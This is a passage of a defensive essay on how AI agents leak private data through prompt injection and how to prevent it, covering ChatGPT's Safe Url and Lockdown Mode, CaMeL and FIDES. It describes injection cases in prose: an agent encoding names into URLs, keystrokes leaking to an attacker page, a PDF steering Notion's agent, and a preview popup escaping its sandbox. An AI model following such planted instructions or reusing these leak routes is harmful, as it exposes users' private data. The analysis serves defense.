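ChatGPT's dialog is part of a mechanism OpenAI calls Safe Url, which also includes the index check on public addresses. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), when Safe Url detects that something the assistant learned in the conversation would reach a third party, either the request is blocked or ChatGPT shows the user that information and asks for confirmation. The same mechanism covers page visits and bookmarks in Atlas, OpenAI's browser, and searches and page visits in Deep Research. Small programs that ChatGPT writes in its Canvas editor run in a sandbox, which asks for consent when it detects unexpected communication.

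A dialog that shows the data being sent is better than one that only asks "Allow this connection?", because a user who sees a colleague's home address has a reason to refuse. Showing the data helps much less if it is unreadable. In ShadowLeak, the model encoded the name and address before sending them, so a dialog that displayed the raw URL would have shown random-looking characters. If an attack leaked the data one letter at a time, each dialog would show one ordinary link.

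The attacker can also prepare the user for the question. OpenAI reproduces an email that presents the theft as a routine step in which the assistant submits an employee's details to a "compliance validation system". A user who has just asked about the company's process for new employees might well expect such a request.

OpenAI's post doesn't report how often users confirm. Evidence from other products suggests that the rate depends heavily on design. *Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) measured how users responded to more than 25 million browser warnings. Users clicked through about 70 percent of Chrome's warnings about insecure connections but only a third of Firefox's, and through fewer than a quarter of either browser's malware and phishing warnings. Anthropic reported in 2026 that Claude Code's users approve about 93 percent of its permission prompts. This shows that users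 are used to approving prompts, but not that they are careless, since most of the prompts were presumably for harmless commands.

A dialog should therefore appear rarely, name the receiving host, and show the decoded data. When the user probably can't judge the request, blocking it is safer than asking.

### Data that leaves before the question

A dialog also has to appear before the data leaves, and developers can misjudge when that is. Operator, a browser agent that OpenAI released in January 2025, asked for confirmation before important steps such as submitting a form. Rehberger's Embrace The Red post *ChatGPT Operator* (2025) showed that a web page can receive text before a form is submitted. A script on his page sent each character to his server as Operator typed it.

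Planted text led Operator to a site where the user was logged in. The agent copied a private email address from the account page and pasted it into the text box on Rehberger's page. Operator did not ask the user for confirmation because there was no form to submit, and the server had the address before a user could have noticed. OpenAI later merged Operator into ChatGPT's agent mode and closed the separate product. Any browser agent that asks only before submitting a form has the same weakness. Its developers need to treat typing into an outside page as sending data and have the agent ask before the first keystroke.

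Some leaks happen without the user being asked, because the product doesn't recognise them as transfers. One example is the DNS leak that Check Point reported in ChatGPT's code environment, which OpenAI fixed in February 2026. According to the firm's explanation, quoted in The Hacker News, the model treated the environment as unable to send data out, so it did not block the transfer or raise it with the user. No warning appeared.

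### How often models resist

Developers train models to refuse planted instructions. OpenAI writes that most of the attacks it knows of against ChatGPT fail for this reason, before Safe Url is needed. But the compliance email, which outside researchers reported in 2025, worked in half of the tests. Radware reported that a closely similar email, used in ShadowLeak, worked every time, so small changes in wording or set-up may matter as much as the model.

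Anthropic's system cards, the safety reports it publishes with each model, give attack success rates by number of attempts. The card for Claude Opus 4.5 (November 2025) reports results for a set of strong attacks from the security firm Gray Swan. A single attempt succeeded 4.7 percent of the time. The chance that at least one attempt succeeded was 33.6 percent with ten attempts and 63.0 percent with a hundred.

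If each attempt succeeds independently with probability p, the chance that at least one of n attempts works is

1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

With p = 0.047, this gives 38 percent for ten attempts, which is close to the measured figure, but 99 percent for a hundred, which is far above it. The attempts are therefore not independent. Nearly every attack seems to fail in some scenarios, while in others one succeeds after a few attempts. Even when the average success rate is low, the model can be easy to fool on a particular task, and an attacker who finds that task can use it repeatedly.

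Attack success also depends on the setting. In the system card for Claude Opus 4.6 (February 2026), attacks on a coding agent never succeeded in 200 attempts. When the model operated a computer through its screen, a single attempt succeeded 17.8 percent of the time. At least one of 200 attempts succeeded 78.6 percent of the time without extra safeguards and 57.1 percent with them. Newer models may score better. Defenders reading those models' cards should look for the success rate at the highest number of attempts, in the setting closest to their own product.

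### Whether a partial defence counts

OpenAI treats model training as one of several layers of defense. It compares an agent to a customer service worker who can give refunds, but whose employer caps them because it expects some customers to deceive the worker. OpenAI also writes that classifiers that screen incoming text usually miss well-developed attacks, because detecting one is as hard as detecting a lie, often without the necessary context.

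Willison objects to relying on layers that work most of the time. In application security, he writes, "99% is a failing grade", because an attacker will find the remaining 1 percent. He was responding to an article in *The Economist* that urged AI developers to think like Victorian engineers, who overbuilt their bridges because they couldn't trust the iron. Unlike poor iron, an attacker searches for weak points. If an attack works 1 percent of the time and the attempts are independent, a hundred attempts give a 63 percent chance of at least one success. An attacker who sends one email each to 10,000 users can expect about a hundred victims without retrying.

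Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), in *The Attacker Moves Second*, support him with experiments. They designed attacks specifically for each of 12 published defences, most of which had attack success rates near zero in their original evaluations. The new attacks succeeded more than 90 percent of the time against most of the defences. The defences had looked strong because they were tested on fixed sets of attacks that did not adapt to them.

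Both sides agree that the system should limit the damage when the model is fooled, but they differ on how much a filter adds once that limit is in place. A filter helps because each attack the model refuses is one fewer dialog for a user to misjudge, and failed attempts give the defender a chance to notice the attack. Someone judging whether a URL channel is closed should still assume that the model follows the attacker's instructions.

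### Separating secrets, untrusted text and the network

Willison's answer is to remove one part of the lethal trifecta. The Notion case he describes had all three parts. In September 2025, the researcher Abi Raghuram showed how a PDF with hidden text could mislead the new agent in Notion, a workspace for documents and databases. The agent read a list of clients, put their names and revenues into a URL, and passed the URL to its search tool, which accepted URLs as well as search terms. Willison suggested that Notion stop the search tool from accepting URLs, but he doesn't report a fix.

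The simplest way to keep secrets away from untrusted text is to give no private data to an agent that reads it. A company can run web research in a session with no connected mailbox or client database, and paste in only what the task needs. Coding agents usually need some credentials, so Willison recommends giving them test accounts with strict spending limits, which limit the loss if a key is stolen.

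An application can also change the agent's permissions during a session. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) proposes that, unless a person supervises it, an agent should combine at most two of the following in one session: untrusted input, private data, and the ability to change things or communicate externally. For example, an agent could browse freely until it opens the client list, then lose network access for the rest of the session.

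The application has to enforce this outside the model and treat anything that could contain a stranger's text as untrusted. Email is a hard case because a mailbox contains both private data and untrusted text. Under this rule, a mail assistant loses network access as soon as it reads its first message. Starting a new session restores access only if no text or memory carries over from the old one.

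A finer form of separation tracks individual pieces of data instead of whole sessions. Willison proposed an early version, the dual LLM pattern, in 2023. A privileged model with tools receives only the user's request, and a quarantined model without tools processes the untrusted text. The privileged model refers to the quarantined model's answers by variable name, without access to their contents.

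Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues (2025), in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, pointed out a gap in this approach. Suppose the user asks the agent to send Bob the document he requested in the last meeting. The quarantined model finds Bob's address in the meeting notes. Planted text in the notes can't change the plan, but it can make the quarantined model return the attacker's address, and the privileged model then sends the document there. Their system, CaMeL, closes the gap by having the privileged model write the plan as a program. A custom interpreter runs the program, records where each value came from and who may see it, and checks a policy before each tool call.

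### One request, step by step

Information-flow control, the older computer security technique behind CaMeL, attaches a label to every value. A simple label has two parts, whether the value comes only from trusted sources and who may read it. When a program computes a value c from a and b, the labels combine:

readers(c) = readers(a) ∩ readers(b)

trusted(c) = trusted(a) and trusted(b)

A fetch or search is allowed only if everyone who could see the request is among the readers of its arguments.

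Take a request like the one in the Notion case. A user uploads a supplier's PDF and asks the agent to summarise it, look up the supplier on the web, and say whether the supplier is already a client. A simplified plan might look like this:

```
doc      = read_file("proposal.pdf")
supplier = reader(doc, "Which company wrote this?")
results  = web_search(supplier)
clients  = read_table("clients")
match    = lookup(clients, supplier)
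answer   = reader([doc, results, match], "Write a summary")
show_user(answer)
```

The privileged model writes the program before any tool has read the PDF. `reader` is the quarantined model, which can return text but can't call tools. The interpreter assigns these labels:

| Value | Comes from | Trusted | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|---|
| `doc` | The supplier | No | Anyone |
| `supplier` | `doc` | No | Anyone |
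| `results` | The web | No | Anyone |
| `clients` | The company's database | Yes | The user's team |
| `match` | `clients` and `supplier` | No | The user's team |
| `answer` | `doc`, `results` and `match` | No | The user's team |

If the PDF contains hidden text like Raghuram's, the quarantined model may obey it. But that model has no tool that opens the client list, and the program already fixes which tools run and in what order. The worst the model can do in the second line is return a false company name or a URL. That URL could contain only text from the PDF, which the supplier already has, so `web_search(supplier)` can go ahead.

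If the privileged model had written a plan that searched the web for `match`, the interpreter would block the search because the search provider isn't in the user's team. The interpreter makes that decision without using a model, so rewording the planted text can't change it.

This example can still go wrong in two ways. Someone has to label the PDF as readable by anyone. If the application labels every uploaded file as private, which is the cautious default, the interpreter will refuse the supplier search and the user will get a dialog. The last `reader` call also mixes private data with planted instructions, so the summary may be wrong, and it may contain a Markdown image with the client's details in the address. The chat window that displays `answer` has to obey the same labels, or it could leak those details by loading the image.

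Labels on values also miss information that leaks through which steps a program runs. Suppose a plan searches for the supplier only if it is a client. Anyone may read the `supplier` value it passes, but the search reveals that the client list contains that name, which is one bit of information. A loop that makes one request per client would reveal the number of clients. CaMeL has a strict mode that also labels whatever happens inside such a branch or loop, but this mode refuses more plans. Debenedetti and colleagues acknowledge that other side channels remain, such as the timing of requests.

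### What separation costs

CaMeL's developers tested it on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 everyday tasks in email, banking, travel and team chat. It solved 77 percent of the tasks with its security guarantee, compared with 84 percent for the same kind of agent without a defence. It also used nearly three times as many tokens in the median task, because it makes extra model calls and sometimes has to rewrite a failed program.

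A loss of seven percentage points is modest, but AgentDojo's tasks use a fixed set of documented tools. In a real product, someone has to write policies for each tool. When a policy refuses a legitimate action, the usual fallback is to ask the user, so poor policies would bring back frequent warnings.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes a different approach, FIDES, developed at Microsoft. The agent still plans one step at a time, as most commercial agents do, and carries a label for everything in its context. When a tool returns untrusted text, FIDES can store it in a variable so that the model doesn't read it and the context stays trusted. If the agent needs a fact from the variable, a quarantined model can answer within a fixed type, such as yes or no, which leaves little room for instructions. If the agent reads the text itself,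 its context is labelled untrusted, and the policy then blocks tools that require a trusted context. On AgentDojo, hiding text in this way let an agent complete a wider range of tasks under the policies.

Both systems need a person's approval for some tasks. For example, if the user asks the agent to do whatever an email requests, the action has to come from the untrusted text.

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025), by Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, describes simpler designs for narrower agents. Its rule is that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any consequential action. The paper presents ten case studies and discusses the trade-offs, but doesn't measure how many tasks agents can no longer complete under each design.

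| Pattern | How it works | What can still leak through a URL |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from fixed actions and never sees their results | The choice of action, which untrusted text can't influence |
| Plan then execute | The agent fixes its tool calls before reading untrusted text | Private data in the arguments of a planned fetch |
| Map-reduce | A separate model without tools reads each document and returns a restricted answer | Whatever the restricted answer can influence |
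| Dual LLM | A privileged model handles untrusted text only as variables | Private data, if a variable that contains it reaches a fetch |
| Code then execute | The model writes a program, as in CaMeL | Depends on whether the interpreter checks labels |
| Context minimisation | The application removes text from the context once it has served its purpose | Anything left in the context |

The second row is easy to overlook. An agent that plans to "read the mail, then open the calendar page" has fixed which tools it will use, but not necessarily the page's address. The fetch also needs a fixed URL or a check on the URL passed to it.

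*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Mullins and colleagues, 2026) extends the idea to agents that work by looking at a screen and clicking. A trusted model writes a complete plan, with branches for different situations, before the agent sees the screen. The agent kept up to 57 percent of a leading model's performance on OSWorld, a benchmark of desktop tasks, which is a much larger loss than CaMeL's on AgentDojo. The researchers also describe "branch steering", in which a misleading screen element sends the agent down a branch that the plan allows but the situation doesn't call for. If the branches open different addresses, the attacker can again choose which prepared link the agent opens.

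### Lockdown Mode

Some users can switch off the features that let their assistant send data out. OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode for ChatGPT's enterprise plans in February 2026. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*, the company began rolling the setting out to personal accounts on June 4. The setting targets only the outgoing request, the last step of an attack, so planted text can still reach the model and distort its answers.

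| Feature | With Lockdown Mode on |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | Cached content only, so results may be old or missing |
| Images | ChatGPT may not show images in ordinary answers or fetch them from the web |
| Deep Research and Agent Mode | Off |
| Canvas | Users can't approve network access for the code |
| File downloads for data analysis | Off; users can still upload files |
| Connected apps, personal and self-serve Business accounts | Synced data only; no live access or write actions |
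| Connected apps, managed workspaces | Whatever the administrator allows |
| Memory, file uploads and chat sharing | Unchanged |
| Network access in Codex | Unchanged |

Cached browsing has the advantage described earlier for stored copies, because the attacker's server receives no request.

Willison (2026) welcomed the setting because its limits are deterministic and don't depend on an AI system that an attack could subvert. He added that its existence implies ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly protect against a determined attacker. OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, presented it as a trade-off worth making for people at elevated risk.

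The connected-apps rows need the most attention from companies. Help Net Security's *OpenAI is locking down parts of ChatGPT to reduce data theft risks* (2026) reports that OpenAI advises administrators to review each app and action before enabling it. Synced data carries the least risk because querying it causes no live requests. OpenAI advises against access to untrusted apps. It also warns about write actions in trusted apps when many people can see the results or the administrator can't tell who can see them.

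#### The popup flaw

Lockdown Mode left one way to send data out, through the preview ChatGPT can show of an HTML page it has written. Check Point disclosed this in the autumn of 2026, and The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) quotes the firm's explanation.

1. ChatGPT placed the preview in nested frames, which are pages inside a page, and a sandbox kept them from contacting outside servers without the user's consent.
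2. ChatGPT intercepted attempts by the previewed page to open a new window.
3. The sandbox's own permissions still allowed popups, and allowed them to escape the sandbox.
4. The researchers' page created another frame inside itself. That frame had its own, unmodified function for opening windows.
5. The popup opened outside the sandbox, where neither its restrictions nor Lockdown Mode's applied.

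An attacker could start the attack with a crafted prompt, a malicious custom GPT or a shared chat. According to Clubic's *Même avec son mode de verrouillage activé, ChatGPT laissait fuiter des conversations*, the flaw was worst in ChatGPT Classic, OpenAI's older desktop app, because its built-in browser opened windows without any user action. Just chatting with the attacker's GPT could send the user's messages to the attacker's server, with no sign on the screen. The popup could also show a fake ChatGPT update, though the user had to click to download the malware. The headline of TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* refers to the "entire chat history", but the Check Point statements quoted in the article don't go that far.

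OpenAI fixed the flaw on September 18, 2026. Clubic reports that OpenAI removed the two sandbox permissions and that Check Point's technique failed when the researchers retried it. Removing the permissions is a sounder repair than intercepting the function in more places, because the browser enforces them on every frame, including those a page creates later.

A week before Check Point's disclosure, Parameter Labs described a different flaw in the same component. If a victim opened a shared ChatGPT link and clicked its preview, the attacker's code could run with the victim's logged-in session. Two serious flaws in one preview feature are a good reason for Lockdown Mode, which is meant for sensitive data, to turn the preview off, as it already does with Agent Mode. Until then, administrators can include the preview in their own leak tests, using a page that tries to open a window to a test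 server. They should test each app their staff use, since the flaw needed no click in ChatGPT Classic, which OpenAI will keep running until January 30, 2027.
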